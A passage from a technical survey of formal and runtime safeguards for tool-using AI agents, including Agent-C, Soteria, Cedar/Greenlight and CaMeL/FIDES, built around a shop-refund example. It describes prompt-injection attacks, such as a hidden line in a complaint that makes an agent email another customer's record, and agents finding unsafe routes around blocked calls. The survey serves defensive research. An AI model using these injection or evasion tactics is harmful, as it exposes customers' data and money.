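With Agent-C, every model followed the rules in every task. This is expected from the theorems, since the researchers measured compliance with the same policies they had encoded as rules. The completion rates are more informative, and they rise in every row, most for the weaker models. Part of the increase comes from the definition of completion, which counts a task as a failure if the agent completes it by breaking a rule. The figures don't show how many of the extra tasks the agent would otherwise have left unfinished.

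The researchers also wrote 17 attacks for each domain, in which the customer asks for something the policy forbids. Without Agent-C, Claude Sonnet 4.5 carried out the harmful request in 5 of the 17 retail attacks. With Agent-C, no attack succeeded on any model. By the formula for clean test records, 17 clean trials would support an upper bound of only about 16% on the failure rate. The theorems give a much stronger guarantee, but only for calls the rules forbid, so the attacks mainly test whether the rules cover the harmful requests.

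Agent-C takes time. With Qwen3-32B, an ordinary task took 480 seconds on average, compared with 333 seconds without safeguards.

### Simpler rules, warnings and training

AgentSpec, an earlier system, uses rules made up of a trigger, a condition to test and a response, such as blocking the call. In tests by Kamath and colleagues, it raised the open models' average compliance from 38% to 82%, but it failed to enforce some of the airline's restrictions on cancellations and did not ensure that agents authenticated customers first. With Qwen3-32B, agents still completed slightly more airline tasks within the rules under AgentSpec (38.7%) than under Agent-C (35.8%). Kamath and colleagues wrote the AgentSpec rules themselves, so AgentSpec's results depend partly on how well they used a rule language they had not designed.

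Elkoussy and Perez use one set of temporal rules for three purposes. Their system, AgentLTL, can score a finished run, block calls during a run, or supply the reward for training a model. Each rule has a weight, and the score is

1 − (total weight of violated rules) / (total weight of all rules).

AgentLTL blocks calls using only the rules that an unfinished trace can definitely violate, and checks the others when the run ends. In its milder mode, it blocks a call and warns the model, but lets the call through if the model repeats it. This doesn't guarantee that the model follows the rules, but the average score rose for five of the seven models and fell slightly for the other two. DeepSeek-V4-Flash improved from 0.60 to 0.87. The stricter mode ends the run after three violations of the same rule. Three models scored lower in this mode than with no blocking, including DeepSeek-V4-Flash at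 0.53, because a model can't recover once its run has ended.

Stopping a run can also cause harm outside a test. Elkoussy and Perez warn that ending a transaction halfway may leave a system in an inconsistent state. If the monitor ends the run after the shop's agent cancels an order but before the refund, the customer loses the money and doesn't get the kettle.

For the third purpose, they trained a small model, Qwen3-4B-Instruct, with a reward based half on the compliance score and half on correct answers and similarity to a model solution. On the full benchmark, its accuracy rose from 13% to 57% and its compliance from 0.56 to 0.78. It also improved on procedures unlike those in training, which suggests it learned more than particular sequences. Such training could reduce the number of calls a monitor has to block, but an agent that scores 0.78 still breaks many rules. The benchmark's tools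 do only simple arithmetic and never fail, so the gains may be smaller with real tools.

### Checking a plan before it runs

A monitor has access only to the calls made so far. *SOTERIA* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026) addresses this by having the model write a plan and checking it before any tool runs. The plan is a small program with tool calls, conditions and branches.

The check relies on *tool contracts*, similar to those *AI Agent Systems* suggests. Each contract has a *precondition* for a call's inputs and a *postcondition* for its result. For example, a payment tool might require a positive amount and a valid payment method, and guarantee a confirmation number. With these contracts, a verifier can work out what could happen at each point in a plan without running the tools.

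He and colleagues give the example of a plan for cancelling a flight reservation. The agent looks up the reservation, calculates how long ago the customer booked, cancels if this was within the last 24 hours and refuses otherwise. The plan breaks the airline's rules, which also require the agent to check first that the customer hasn't already flown part of the trip.

Soteria translates the plan and the rules into Dafny, a language with a built-in verifier, and adds a log of calls that exists only for the proof. At the end of every path through the plan, each cancellation in the log must come after a check showing that no flight on the same reservation has been flown. The faulty plan has a path on which the agent cancels without making this check. Dafny reports the error, and the model gets up to eight attempts to repair the plan. Dafny also checks that every call meets its tool's precondition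 and that the plan can't get stuck at a point where no branch applies. Plans aren't allowed to loop back to an earlier state, so the number of paths is finite.

A plan makes it possible to verify liveness rules, because it contains the future steps that a monitor lacks. Dafny can prove that an email follows the refund on every path through the plan, but the model may depart from the plan when carrying it out. In its usual mode, Soteria treats the plan as guidance and has a monitor check each call against the safety rules. If the model leaves out the email, the monitor detects the omission only at the end. A strict mode allows only the calls in the plan, so it also blocks harmless extra calls, such as looking up a second reservation because the customer asked about it.

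The guarantees depend on the contracts. If a tool returns a result that its postcondition excludes, Soteria aborts the run, because any proof that used the contract may be wrong.

He and colleagues tested Soteria with four models on 207 tasks. These were airline and retail conversations from τ²-bench, a successor to τ-bench, and file and document tasks from the Toolathlon benchmark. They found no rule violations. With Soteria, Claude Opus 4.6 completed 88.0% of airline tasks within the rules, compared with 52.0% without safeguards, and 90.4% of retail tasks, compared with 46.5%. Much of the retail gain seems to have come from guidance. Without a plan, Opus often collected all the information it needed and then passed the customer to a human instead of making the exchange.

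The researchers also added Soteria's parts one by one to measure how much each contributes. The following figures are for airline tasks.

| Configuration | GPT-5.4-mini: completed within the rules | GPT-5.4-mini: violations | Gemini 3 Flash: completed within the rules | Gemini 3 Flash: violations |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Plan without verification | 44% | 13 | 32% | 27 |
| With verification | 46% | 10 | 32% | 24 |
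| With reusable, verified sub-plans as well | 50% | 12 | 38% | 22 |
| With the monitor as well | 60% | 0 | 62% | 0 |

Verification added little on its own. A proof about a plan is of limited use if the model doesn't follow the plan. The monitor accounted for the largest gain with both models.

Some of He and colleagues' results count against their conclusion that "safety and utility need not be traded off". On the Toolathlon tasks, Opus completed 30.2% without safeguards, including those in which it broke a rule, and 18.6% with Soteria. They also repeated the airline test five times with GPT-5.4-mini, allowing only three attempts at planning. The model completed 50.8% of tasks within the rules with Soteria and 48.0% with AgentSpec, with overlapping confidence intervals. However, AgentSpec allowed about four violations per run of 50 tasks, while Soteria allowed none.

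Soteria is also expensive in conversations, because the model writes a new plan at each turn. An airline task with Opus cost about $0.80, compared with $0.32 without safeguards. The researchers corrected some of their rules while auditing the results, so a business using a first draft of its rules might do worse.

### The verifier tax

Other researchers have found that blocking unsafe calls can leave agents doing very little useful work. *The Verifier Tax* (2026) describes experiments on τ-bench with two fairly small models, GPT-OSS-20B and GLM-4-9B, in which a verifier assessed each proposed action before it ran. This multiplied token use by 2.0 to 2.8. According to *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, a systematic review of 38 studies by Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026), the verifier blocked 94% of unsafe actions, but in most settings the agents completed fewer than 5% of tasks both safely and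 correctly.

According to Dantas and colleagues, this happened because the agents found other unsafe routes. If the harness blocks a refund to an unverified customer, for example, the shop's agent might email him a voucher instead. Blocking removes one unsafe step but gives the agent no safe way to finish the task. Even with a 94% success rate at blocking, an agent that keeps trying may also get an unsafe step through. If it makes ten unsafe attempts and the verifier independently catches each with 94% probability, at least one gets through in 46% of runs.

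The result comes from a single study, and Dantas and colleagues say it needs independent replication. They give seven of their review's nine main claims the lowest rating for certainty, meaning that further studies are likely to produce substantially different figures.

Agent-C's results on the same benchmark are far better, and model size doesn't explain the difference. Qwen3-8B is smaller than both models in *The Verifier Tax*, yet with Agent-C it completed 42.1% of retail tasks and 39.3% of airline tasks within the rules. One likely reason is that Agent-C blocks every call its rules forbid, whereas Dantas and colleagues class the verifier in *The Verifier Tax* among methods without a single formal basis. Agent-C also has the model rewrite a rejected call immediately, and Soteria provides a plan to return to. Conversation limits may matter too. *The Verifier Tax* allowed one model 15 turns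 and the other 30, so repeated refusals could have used up much of a conversation, while Soteria's agents had up to 100 steps.

The data on Agent-C and Soteria suggest a smaller loss in task completion. Kamath et al. also tested DynaGuard, a language model that judges calls against a written policy. On retail tasks with Qwen3-32B, it raised compliance from 38% to 77% but reduced the share of tasks completed within the rules from 25.5% to 9.6%. He et al. used four models to compare Soteria with three safeguards that check calls without a verified plan. Adding one of these three safeguards reduced the number of retail tasks completed within the rules in 11 of the 12 combinations of model and safeguard, but increased the number of airline tasks completed within the rules in 7 of the 12.

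So blocking alone can reduce useful work, though usually by much less than in *The Verifier Tax*, and the effect varies with the task. The better figures for Agent-C and Soteria come from their own developers. These studies also used different models, rules and limits on conversation length, so measuring how much a second attempt or a plan helps would require a test that holds all of these fixed.

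## Proving what an agent's permissions allow

Agent-C and Soteria can block a forbidden call only if the call passes through them and somebody has written a rule against it. A developer who says that an agent can't break its permissions may therefore mean one of three things. The first is that the software enforces every rule, so the shop's harness never pays a refund that a rule forbids. The second is that the rules also leave no gap, so they never permit a refund to an unverified customer. The third is that the agent is safe, so neither the shop nor its customers will come to harm. Researchers have proved enforcement for a small agent framework, and Amazon now sells tools that search for gaps in rules, but neither kind of proof shows that an agent is safe.

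### A proof about the software around the model

*Containment Verification* addresses enforcement. It assumes *effect exclusivity*, meaning that every effect the agent can have on the outside world passes through one typed interface. A typed interface accepts only actions of a fixed form. The shop's interface would accept four kinds of action, and a refund would have to consist of a customer and an amount. If the interface also accepted arbitrary computer commands, a proof about it would guarantee very little.

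The Dafny program represents the language model as a procedure with no code inside. The procedure specifies only the type of its return value, so Dafny has to check the rest of the program for every value of that type.

At each step, the software is in some state s, receives an action a, produces an event e and moves to a new state s′. The event might be "paid $40 to customer 17". If the software rejects the action, the event has no effect. A policy is a condition Π(s, a, e, s′) that every step must meet. For the shop, Π could require that if e is a refund to a customer, that customer is in *Verified* in state s.

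The theorem concerns two descriptions of the software, a simple abstract model and a more detailed model of how it operates. It has two conditions:

- In the abstract model, every step satisfies the policy, whatever sequence of actions arrives.
- The detailed model *refines* the abstract one. The two start in matching states, and for every step of the detailed model, the abstract model has a step with the same action and a matching event that leads to a matching state. If the abstract step satisfies the policy, so does the detailed one.

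Every step of every run of the detailed model therefore satisfies the policy. To prove this, we build a matching abstract run for any detailed run, one step at a time, from the same actions. Each abstract step satisfies the policy by the first condition, so by the second condition, the matching detailed step does too.

The theorem holds for all sequences of typed actions, and therefore for any AI model, prompt or attack that could produce them. It does not cover effects that bypass the interface. A corollary extends the result to the running system, but only if its every visible effect corresponds to an event in the formal model. The proof assumes effect exclusivity without evidence.

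### What the proof covers in practice

The researchers applied the theorem to PocketFlow, a 100-line framework for building agents. They proved that an agent can read files only inside one folder, call only tools on an approved list, and run for at most a fixed number of steps. This policy checks only the name of the tool being called, so it would allow a $5,000 refund if the shop put refunds on the approved list. The theorem also allows conditions on a tool's arguments, so the shop could add its $200 limit, but it would need a new proof.

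Experts used to write such proofs by hand, which took so much work that few systems had one. In this study, two Claude models wrote the specification, the detailed model and the proof, and Dafny checked the result. Four runs on two example agents used between 1.6 and 3.4 million tokens each, and Dafny checked each path through an agent in at most 2.5 seconds. When the researchers compiled the verified program into Python and gave it a mixture of permitted and forbidden actions, it recorded only permitted events. These tests offer some evidence about the compiled program, which matters because the proof doesn't cover concurrency, timing or hardware faults.

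A language model that writes its own specification might just describe what the code already does, and then the proof would be worthless. To prevent this, the researchers had the model write the safety requirement without seeing the code. Each specification also had to pass three checks before the final proof. It had to be valid Dafny, and two damaged versions of the proof, one with its content removed and one with a planted error, had to fail.

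For comparison, the process was repeated with the code visible to the model writing the specification. One of the example agents may read only documents on an approved list, but the specification template had a field only for tool calls, not for documents. With the code visible, the model left the list of tool calls empty. The requirement "every tool call is on the approved list" was then true because there were no tool calls, and nothing limited which documents the agent read. This specification still passed all three checks, and Dafny proved it. Without the code, the model had recorded document reads as tool calls, so its requirement did limit them.

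The shop could make the same mistake. If its agent can also issue vouchers but the formal model never records any, Dafny will still prove that every recorded voucher went to a verified customer. *Containment Verification* recommends also checking that each part of a requirement applies to something that can happen in the model.

### Verifying agent skills

PocketFlow's approved list doesn't cover what a tool does once the agent calls it. That gap matters for *skills*, which are packages of written instructions, often with scripts, that an agent can load to carry out a procedure. The shop might download a skill for damaged goods that includes a script for resizing customers' photographs. *Skills as Verifiable Artifacts* (2026) proposes that each skill should come with a level of verification and a list of the capabilities it needs, such as reading files or contacting a website. A person must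 approve every irreversible call by an unverified skill. For a verified skill, a person approves only calls outside the declared capabilities, so a mistaken verification removes a human check that might have caught the problem.

Metere (2026), in *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills*, combines three methods to justify the highest level:

- Static analysis reads each script without running it and computes a set of effects that includes everything the script could do. If a script builds and runs new code, the analysis assumes that it could do anything.
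- A *refinement type*, a data type with a logical condition attached, restricts the function that carries out tool calls. The function accepts a call only if its capability is on the declared list.
- A solver searches for a session of up to about 100 calls in which something in the world changes without a matching approved call in the log.

In Metere's example, a skill fetches a web page and summarises it. The skill declares two capabilities, but static analysis finds that its script also writes to a folder of temporary files. The operator can then declare the missing capability or change the script. Such mismatches are probably common, because people update scripts and forget to update the declarations.

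Metere's combined theorem is stronger than its proof supports. It states that no undeclared capability appears in a session's trace, even in a call that the harness refuses. But a language model can still request an undeclared capability, and the refinement type only stops the harness from carrying out the request. The proof does support the weaker conclusion that no undeclared effect takes place, which is what the shop needs.

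The published software is also weaker than the theory. By default, it replaces the static analyser with searches for text patterns, the refinement type with an ordinary check at run time, and the solver with a program that tries every sequence. The theorem requires an analyser that never misses an effect, but a pattern can miss one written in an unusual way. Trying every sequence is feasible for up to 10 capabilities and 8 calls, or about 200 million sequences. The example skill ends up with only three capabilities, but 100 calls would still give 4^100 sequences, which is more than 10^60. The software passes its 53 tests, but that doesn't make the pattern search a sound analysis. Operators can replace the defaults with stronger tools, and would have to do so before relying on the theorem.

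### Permissions as formulas

Amazon's cloud business, AWS, offers permission checks as a commercial service. Its platform for running agents, Bedrock AgentCore, became generally available in October 2025, and policy controls followed in preview, according to S&P Global (2026). AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026) announced the full release of those controls in March 2026. A gateway sits between the agent and its tools, and AWS states that the policy feature checks all agent traffic through the gateway. This again assumes effect exclusivity, because the feature can't check a call that takes another route.

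The rules are written in Cedar, AWS's open-source language for permissions. *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* explains how it works. Each rule permits or forbids certain requests. The gateway refuses any request that no rule permits, and a rule that forbids a request overrides any rule that permits it, so the order of the rules doesn't matter. If the rules would always refuse a tool, the gateway also leaves it off the list it shows the agent.

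Cedar has no loops and keeps no memory of earlier requests. This makes decisions fast and lets software turn each rule into a logical formula, but rules about sequences of requests need other software to supply the history. For example, if a rule requires a verified customer, the request must include the customer's verification status. Metere points out that Cedar's evaluator, the program that applies the rules to a request, has been formally verified, whereas Metere's own methods assume that the enforcing software is correct.

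People can write Cedar rules themselves or describe them in plain language for a language model to translate. A first check confirms that the translated rules refer to real tools and arguments. A second, Cedar Analysis, looks for logical faults, such as a rule that can never permit anything because it requires a customer to be in the Gold and Platinum tiers at once. Neither check can confirm that a rule means what its author intended, so a mistranslated rule can pass both.

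Some faults appear only when rules are combined. In one AWS example, a rule permits refunds under $100 for Gold customers, while another forbids refunds under $500 for Gold and Platinum customers. The second rule blocks every refund the first was meant to permit. Cedar Analysis checks all the rules together when a developer attaches them to the gateway, and if it finds such an error, the attachment fails with an explanation.

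The analysis can also compare an old set of rules with a new one. In an AWS example, orders of at least 50 items qualify for a discount unless they include limited editions. Someone changes the exclusion so that it applies to limited editions only in orders of more than 200 items. This loosens the rules even though it adds a condition, because an order for 73 limited-edition items now qualifies. The analysis shows that the new rules permit more discounts and exactly the same refunds.

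### One refund rule and one query

A rule set can be free of conflicts and still permit something the shop wants to prevent. To find this, the shop has to state a goal separately from the rules and check whether any permitted request violates that goal.

Suppose the goal is that only verified customers receive refunds. Let a be the amount of a refund, v the statement that the customer is verified, and p the statement that the customer is in the Platinum tier. The shop begins with one rule, which permits a refund if v is true and a ≤ 200. Later the marketing team adds another, which permits a refund if p is true and a ≤ 500. With ∧ for "and" and ∨ for "or", a request that the rules permit but the goal excludes would have to satisfy

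((v ∧ a ≤ 200) ∨ (p ∧ a ≤ 500)) ∧ ¬v

Given this formula, a solver such as Z3 might return the counterexample p = true, v = false and a = 300, which means that an unverified person with a Platinum account can receive $300. Testers who only tried verified Platinum customers would have missed this case.

If the marketing team adds v to its rule, the formula becomes

((v ∧ a ≤ 200) ∨ (p ∧ v ∧ a ≤ 500)) ∧ ¬v

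Both alternatives now require v to be true, and the last part requires it to be false. The solver therefore reports that the formula has no solution, which is a proof for every customer and every amount.

A better repair is to add a rule that forbids any refund without v. Every permitted refund must then satisfy v, whatever the other rules permit, so the formula always contains v ∧ ¬v. The shop can then add new offers without reopening this gap.

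The proof still depends on where the facts come from. AWS notes that a customer's tier comes from an identity token that the language model can't alter, while arguments such as the size of an order come from the model's own tool call. Yet another of AWS's examples forbids refunds more than 90 days after the order date, and there the order date is one of those arguments. Let d be the age of the order according to the tool call and t its true age. A request that gets round the limit satisfies

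d ≤ 90 ∧ t > 90

One solution is d = 10 and t = 200, so a confused or manipulated model could obtain a refund on a 200-day-old order by supplying the wrong date. Adding the assumption d = t closes the gap, but the refund tool would have to make that assumption true by looking up the date itself.

The query also considers only single requests, so it can't detect repeated refunds for the same kettle. A goal about the total paid for an order would need a model of multiple calls.

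### From Access Analyzer to Greenlight

AWS was asking questions of this kind about cloud settings long before it had agents. Its IAM Access Analyzer works out who can reach which resources in a customer's account, and S3 Block Public Access determines whether a storage area is open to the internet. Access settings can interact in millions of combinations, too many to test one by one, but the settings are all available in a form that a solver can read.

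AWS Greenlight extends this approach to agents. According to Expansión's *Limitar los agentes de IA los haría inservibles* (2026), it has been in preview since 1 December 2026, after AWS's artificial intelligence and automated reasoning teams worked on it together for 18 months. Help Net Security's *AWS Greenlight uses math to stop AI agents from breaking company rules* describes how a company would use it.

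The company first chooses which tools and network destinations the agent may reach, since Greenlight blocks all others by default. It also selects documents, such as procedures and security standards, and a language model drafts rules from them. Greenlight can also draw on records of earlier tool calls. ITWeb's *AWS creates gateway to ‘trust’ AI agents* reports that this is meant to capture unwritten practices. But if the shop's agent has been refunding customers without checking the order number, its records will make that look normal, so a person has to decide which practices to keep.

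Greenlight then checks the draft for conflicts and for routes to resources outside the agent's approved access. It can show that the legal and finance departments want incompatible things, but people have to settle the disagreement. Before accepting a change, the company can see which recorded calls the new rule would have blocked. The shop would see in advance that a stricter limit would stop a large share of legitimate refunds.

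In *A 'Doctor Strange' moment for AI?* (2026), Lichtenberg reports that Shawn Bice, an AWS vice president, used chess to explain the search for counterexamples. Bice compared an airline's agent, which can cancel, refund or change a ticket, to a player whose pieces have fixed moves. The airline adds a rule that no passenger may end up stranded. Greenlight looks for permitted moves that would break the rule, and Bice regards the absence of such moves as the proof.

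The comparison with chess works for permissions but is misleading about what happens to passengers. The rules of chess determine everything that can happen on the board, but a passenger's trip also depends on events the agent doesn't control. For example, an airline could define "not stranded" as holding a confirmed seat on another flight, and prove that the agent never cancels a ticket without booking such a seat. If a storm then grounds the second flight, the passenger is stranded even though the agent followed every rule.

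Once the company approves the rules, Greenlight installs them in the AgentCore gateway or in Strands Box, an open-source *sandbox* (an environment that limits what a program can reach). Both check each call from outside the harness, so an agent can't remove a rule by modifying its own software. In PocketFlow, by contrast, the verified code is the harness itself. The gateway's existing policy feature uses Cedar, but neither Help Net Security nor ITWeb specifies the language of Greenlight's own rules.

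### What AWS promises

AWS's chief executive, Matt Garman, said at the launch that mathematical logic rules out "any way an agent can break a specified rule", ITWeb reports. Bice was more cautious in an interview for Computertrends' *AWS Greenlight staví matematické zábrany kolem agentů s umělou inteligencí*, saying that a proof applies only to the policies and system that an organisation has specified and modelled, and that Greenlight is one tool among several.

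These statements are compatible if we read Garman's narrowly. A gateway that receives every call and applies a correct check will never let through a call that a rule forbids. This claim about enforcement would hold even for foolish rules. A search for counterexamples supports the claim that the rules have no gap, but only relative to the goals that somebody wrote down. Garman also said that the logic leaves no chance of misinterpretation, which can't be true of the whole process when a language model drafts the rules.

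AWS's broader claims do not follow from either result. TechRadar's *'It's truly unlike anything else out there today'* quotes the company as saying that, thanks to Greenlight's accuracy, agents "can be trusted with even high-stakes tasks". AWS argues that rare errors add up, as they did over the shop's 1,000 actions. With an error rate of 0.1% per action, only 37% of 1,000-action runs are free of mistakes. But that rate includes every kind of mistake, and Greenlight blocks only those that break a rule. If half of the mistakes broke a rule and blocking them did no harm, the chance of an error-free run would rise to about 61%. The remaining mistakes would be ones the rules permit, such as refunding $150 for a kettle that works perfectly.

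It is still unclear how well Greenlight works in practice. Delta Air Lines plans to use it to check that its agents follow airline policies, and LoanLogics, a mortgage technology company, wants to check its agents against thousands of lending rules. Help Net Security says that Salesforce, ServiceNow and others are building it into their products or plan to. Enter.co's *AWS Greenlight* says that AWS had not published prices. These reports mention no independent evaluation. A useful one would measure how many of a company's policies the drafted rules capture and how much legitimate work they block. When Computertrends asked how long companies would need to turn their policies into rules, Bice declined to give a general estimate.

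### The trusted base of a permission boundary

Even a perfect set of rules relies on a trusted base. For the shop's agent, it would include the following:

- The operating system. Sandboxes generally depend on it to keep programs apart. *Containment Verification* mentions a flaw in Linux, made public in April 2026, that had let users gain extra privileges for nearly ten years before anyone reported it.
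- The network configuration. It must leave the agent no second route to the payment system. In 2026, agents reached real systems from misconfigured test environments.
- The tools' own code. If the refund tool interprets amounts as pounds, a request for 200 passes the check and pays out more than $200. A tool that sends money twice after a network error would also defeat the limit.
- Credentials. An agent that holds the payment system's password doesn't need the gateway's permission, and a thief with a stolen identity token passes as a verified customer.

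The gateway's settings belong on the list as well. AgentCore has a mode for testing rules. In this mode, AWS explains, the system logs whether it would have refused a call but doesn't refuse it. If the shop forgets to switch this mode off, its proof about the rules remains valid, but the agent can still make payments that the rules forbid.

An attack can also stay within the boundary. Neither *Containment Verification* nor Metere covers the meaning of what an agent writes. The shop has to let its agent send emails, and a rule that permits an email to a verified customer also permits one containing another customer's home address.

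## Tracking untrusted data through an agent

Suppose a fraudster complains to the shop about a broken kettle and hides a line in his message telling the agent to send the record of another customer, Ann, to an email address he supplies. The agent is allowed to send emails and to look up customers, which it must do to handle complaints. The harness allows the look-up and then the email, and the fraudster learns where Ann lives. Each call is acceptable on its own, but together they send text from Ann's record to an address taken from a stranger's message.

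A rule about the email call alone can't easily prevent this. The shop could restrict emails to addresses in its records, but the fraudster may be a customer too. The shop could also search outgoing emails for Ann's details, but the model can reword them. The harness needs to track where each part of the email came from.

### Labels for trust and secrecy

*Information-flow control* attaches labels to data and updates them whenever a program computes something new from it. The method dates from the 1970s. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) applies it to agents, with two labels on each value. The trust label is "untrusted" if an outsider could have influenced the value. The secrecy label lists the people who may read it.

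When a program combines several values, the result is untrusted if any of them was, and only people who may read all of them may read the result. Suppose Ann and the shop may read Ann's record, while Ben and the shop may read Ben's. For a text that draws on both records, the permitted readers are

{Ann, shop} ∩ {Ben, shop} = {shop}

so the harness should not email it to either customer.

Costa and colleagues' system checks these labels before each tool call. A trust rule requires that neither a call with serious consequences nor its arguments derive from untrusted data. A secrecy rule requires every recipient of a piece of data to be one of its permitted readers. The secrecy rule alone would not stop a hidden instruction from triggering an email, but it would limit what the email could reveal. Both rules block the email to the fraudster.

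Language models make this kind of tracking difficult. When ordinary code copies one word of a message, the copy depends only on that word, but a model's reply may depend on anything in its input, so a cautious harness has to treat it as depending on everything. Some researchers try to find out which text caused a reply. Willison, the programmer who named prompt injection, points out that a model receives trusted instructions and untrusted text as a single stream of tokens, and that nobody knows a reliable way to make it follow only the trusted instructions. So once the shop's agent has read a complaint, everything it writes afterwards counts as untrusted, and the trust rule blocks every refund.

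### Noninterference

The strongest guarantee in this field is *noninterference*. For trust, it means that changing the untrusted input must not change any protected action. If t is the trusted input, u and u′ are two possible untrusted inputs, and P gives the protected actions that the agent takes, then

P(t, u) = P(t, u′) for all t, u and u′.

If refunds are protected, the agent must issue the same refunds whatever the complaint says. This prevents a hidden instruction from triggering a refund, but it also prevents an honest report of a broken kettle from doing so. For secrecy, the equivalent rule is that changing Ann's record must not affect anything an outsider can see.

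Noninterference compares two runs, so no single trace can show a violation. It is therefore not a safety property, and a monitor that sees only one run must also block some harmless calls to enforce it.

Information can also leak without anyone copying it. Suppose the agent emails a supplier only if Ann has spent more than $1,000. The supplier learns something about Ann's spending from the arrival of the email, whatever the email contains. This is an *implicit flow*, whereas copying her record into the email would be an *explicit flow*.

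### One model plans and another reads

Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind designed CaMeL to let an agent use untrusted text without taking instructions from it. They built on a proposal by Willison to divide the work between two language models. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how the parts work together:

- The *planner* is a language model that receives the user's request but none of the untrusted data. It writes a program, in a restricted form of Python, that contains all the tool calls for the task.
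- The *reader* is a language model without tools. It reads untrusted text and returns a value, such as a name or a date.
- The *interpreter* is ordinary software that runs the program. It attaches *capabilities* to every value, which record the value's sources and permitted readers.

Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a Python function that checks the arguments and their capabilities and allows or blocks the call.

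At the shop, the trusted request would have to come from an employee, since anyone can write a complaint. Suppose an employee asks the agent to send Ann a list of her orders, using the email address in her latest message. The planner might write:

```
message = read_latest_message("Ann")
address = reader("Find the email address", message)
orders = look_up_orders("Ann")
send_email(address, orders)
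```

The planner writes this program before any software opens the message. If the message contains a hidden request for a $5,000 refund, the request may fool the reader, but the reader has no tools and the program has no step that issues a refund.

A cleverer fraudster writes in Ann's name and gives his own address. The program then runs exactly as planned, and the reader correctly returns the fraudster's address. The capabilities are what stop this attack:

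| Value | Source | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|
| message | incoming message | sender, shop |
| address | incoming message, through the reader | sender, shop |
| orders | customer database | Ann, shop |

The email policy compares the recipient with the permitted readers of the orders. The shop doesn't have this address on file for Ann, so the interpreter blocks the call. It would also block the call if Ann really had changed her address, and the shop would have to confirm the new one another way.

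Because the plan is a program, software can also check it in advance, as Soteria does. Nikolaou and colleagues' system, CaMeLoT, converts a plan into a finite-state machine and searches for a path that breaks a rule. If the shop required trusted recipients, CaMeLoT would reject the plan above before any tool ran and return the faulty path so the planner could try again. Checks that need actual values, such as the permitted readers of a particular record, still happen during the run.

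CaMeL's division of work restricts the agent to the paths in its plan, but it does not achieve noninterference, because untrusted data can influence which of those paths the agent takes. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) defines this guarantee and calls the remaining influence *branch steering*. For example, if the plan issues a refund when the reader reports damage and sends an apology otherwise, a fraudster can get the refund by claiming damage.

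### The cost of CaMeL

Most tests of these defences use AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 tasks in four simulated settings: office work, banking, travel and the messaging service Slack. It also has about 35 attacker goals, which testers hide as instructions in the data the agent reads.

Tests by other groups found that CaMeL stops almost all of these attacks but also prevents the agent from completing many tasks. *ATrust* (2026) reports that an agent using Claude 3.5 Haiku completed 61% of tasks under attack without a defence and 37% with CaMeL. The loss was worst in the travel setting, where completion without an attack fell from 55% to 5%. With CaMeL, only one of the 140 travel attacks succeeded, and none did in the other settings. In *AgentSys* (2026), CaMeL stopped every attack, but the agent completed only 30% of tasks when there was no attack. CaMeL used 6.1 million tokens, while three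 other defences used 2.4 to 3.3 million. Both papers present rivals to CaMeL, so the researchers had less reason to make it perform as well as it could.

*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) reported that agents used about 3.4 million tokens with CaMeL and 1.8 million without a defence on 17 desktop computer tasks. Most of the extra tokens were input, but output grew by a much larger factor, from 13,000 tokens to 456,000. Repeated attempts may explain part of the increase, since the defended agents were allowed up to five attempts at each task.

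Part of the loss comes from planning in advance. Peters-Gill and colleagues tested systems of several agents on 112 industrial maintenance tasks, with CaMeL in each agent but no policies on data. Completion fell by 21.6 percentage points on average across five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. Most failures occurred because the agent discovered partway through that it needed a step its plan didn't include. In some others, a tool returned data for the wrong machine or dates and the agent continued with its plan. Peters-Gill and colleagues expect the loss to shrink as models improve, since better models can anticipate more possible outcomes.

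Policies further reduce the share of tasks that CaMeL completes. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, ran CaMeL three times on each of AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks. Without policies, it completed 67% of runs with GPT-5.2 and 71% with MiMo-v2.5, but with policies it completed only 37.5% with either model. Five of 622 completed attack runs succeeded without policies, and none succeeded with them.

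These studies used different models and policies, so their figures don't give a single estimate of the loss from CaMeL. In all of them, though, it is much larger than the loss from Agent-C's rules, which increased the number of tasks completed within the rules.

### FIDES hides only what it must

FIDES, a system by Costa and colleagues at Microsoft, lets a planner model choose one call at a time using earlier results. It hides only data that would make the planner's later output untrusted. If a tool returns a complaint with a trusted timestamp and untrusted text, the planner receives the timestamp and a variable name in place of the text. It can pass the variable to another tool or query an isolated model about it, in which case the answer goes into a new variable. The planner can also open a variable, but everything it writes after that inherits the variable's label.

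FIDES can make an exception for short answers drawn from untrusted messages. A yes-or-no answer carries one bit of information, a choice among four options carries two, and free text has no fixed limit. A policy may let the planner act on a yes-or-no answer because one bit is too little to hold an instruction. The shop's planner could ask the isolated model whether a complaint reports damage, read the answer and decide on a refund. A fraudster could still lie about the damage, but he couldn't change the refund amount or the account it goes to.

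Costa and colleagues prove *explicit secrecy* rather than noninterference, which they consider too restrictive because it would forbid almost any publicly visible action after the agent had read a secret. Explicit secrecy rules out forbidden explicit flows but allows implicit ones, so an observer who sees which tools the agent calls may still be able to infer something about the secret from its choices.

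In tests with GPT-4o, the researchers counted 152 successful AgentDojo attacks against an ordinary agent and none against FIDES with its rules switched on. The share of tasks completed when there was no attack was as follows.

| Agent | Office work | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no rules | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent with labels and rules | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
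| FIDES with labels and rules | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

The three rows average 84%, 42% and 50%, so hiding data recovers only 8 of the 42 points lost to the rules. FIDES did worse in the travel setting because the rules there rarely blocked the ordinary agent, while GPT-4o often mishandled the variables. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES's travel score rose to 68%, and its average lead over the ordinary agent with rules grew from 8 points to 16. These tests didn't use the exception for short answers.

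On the 17 desktop tasks in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, FIDES cost $76, compared with $5.40 for CaMeL. One likely reason is that FIDES calls its planner again after each step, whereas CaMeL's planner writes the whole program at once.

### A language in which every agent keeps to its labels

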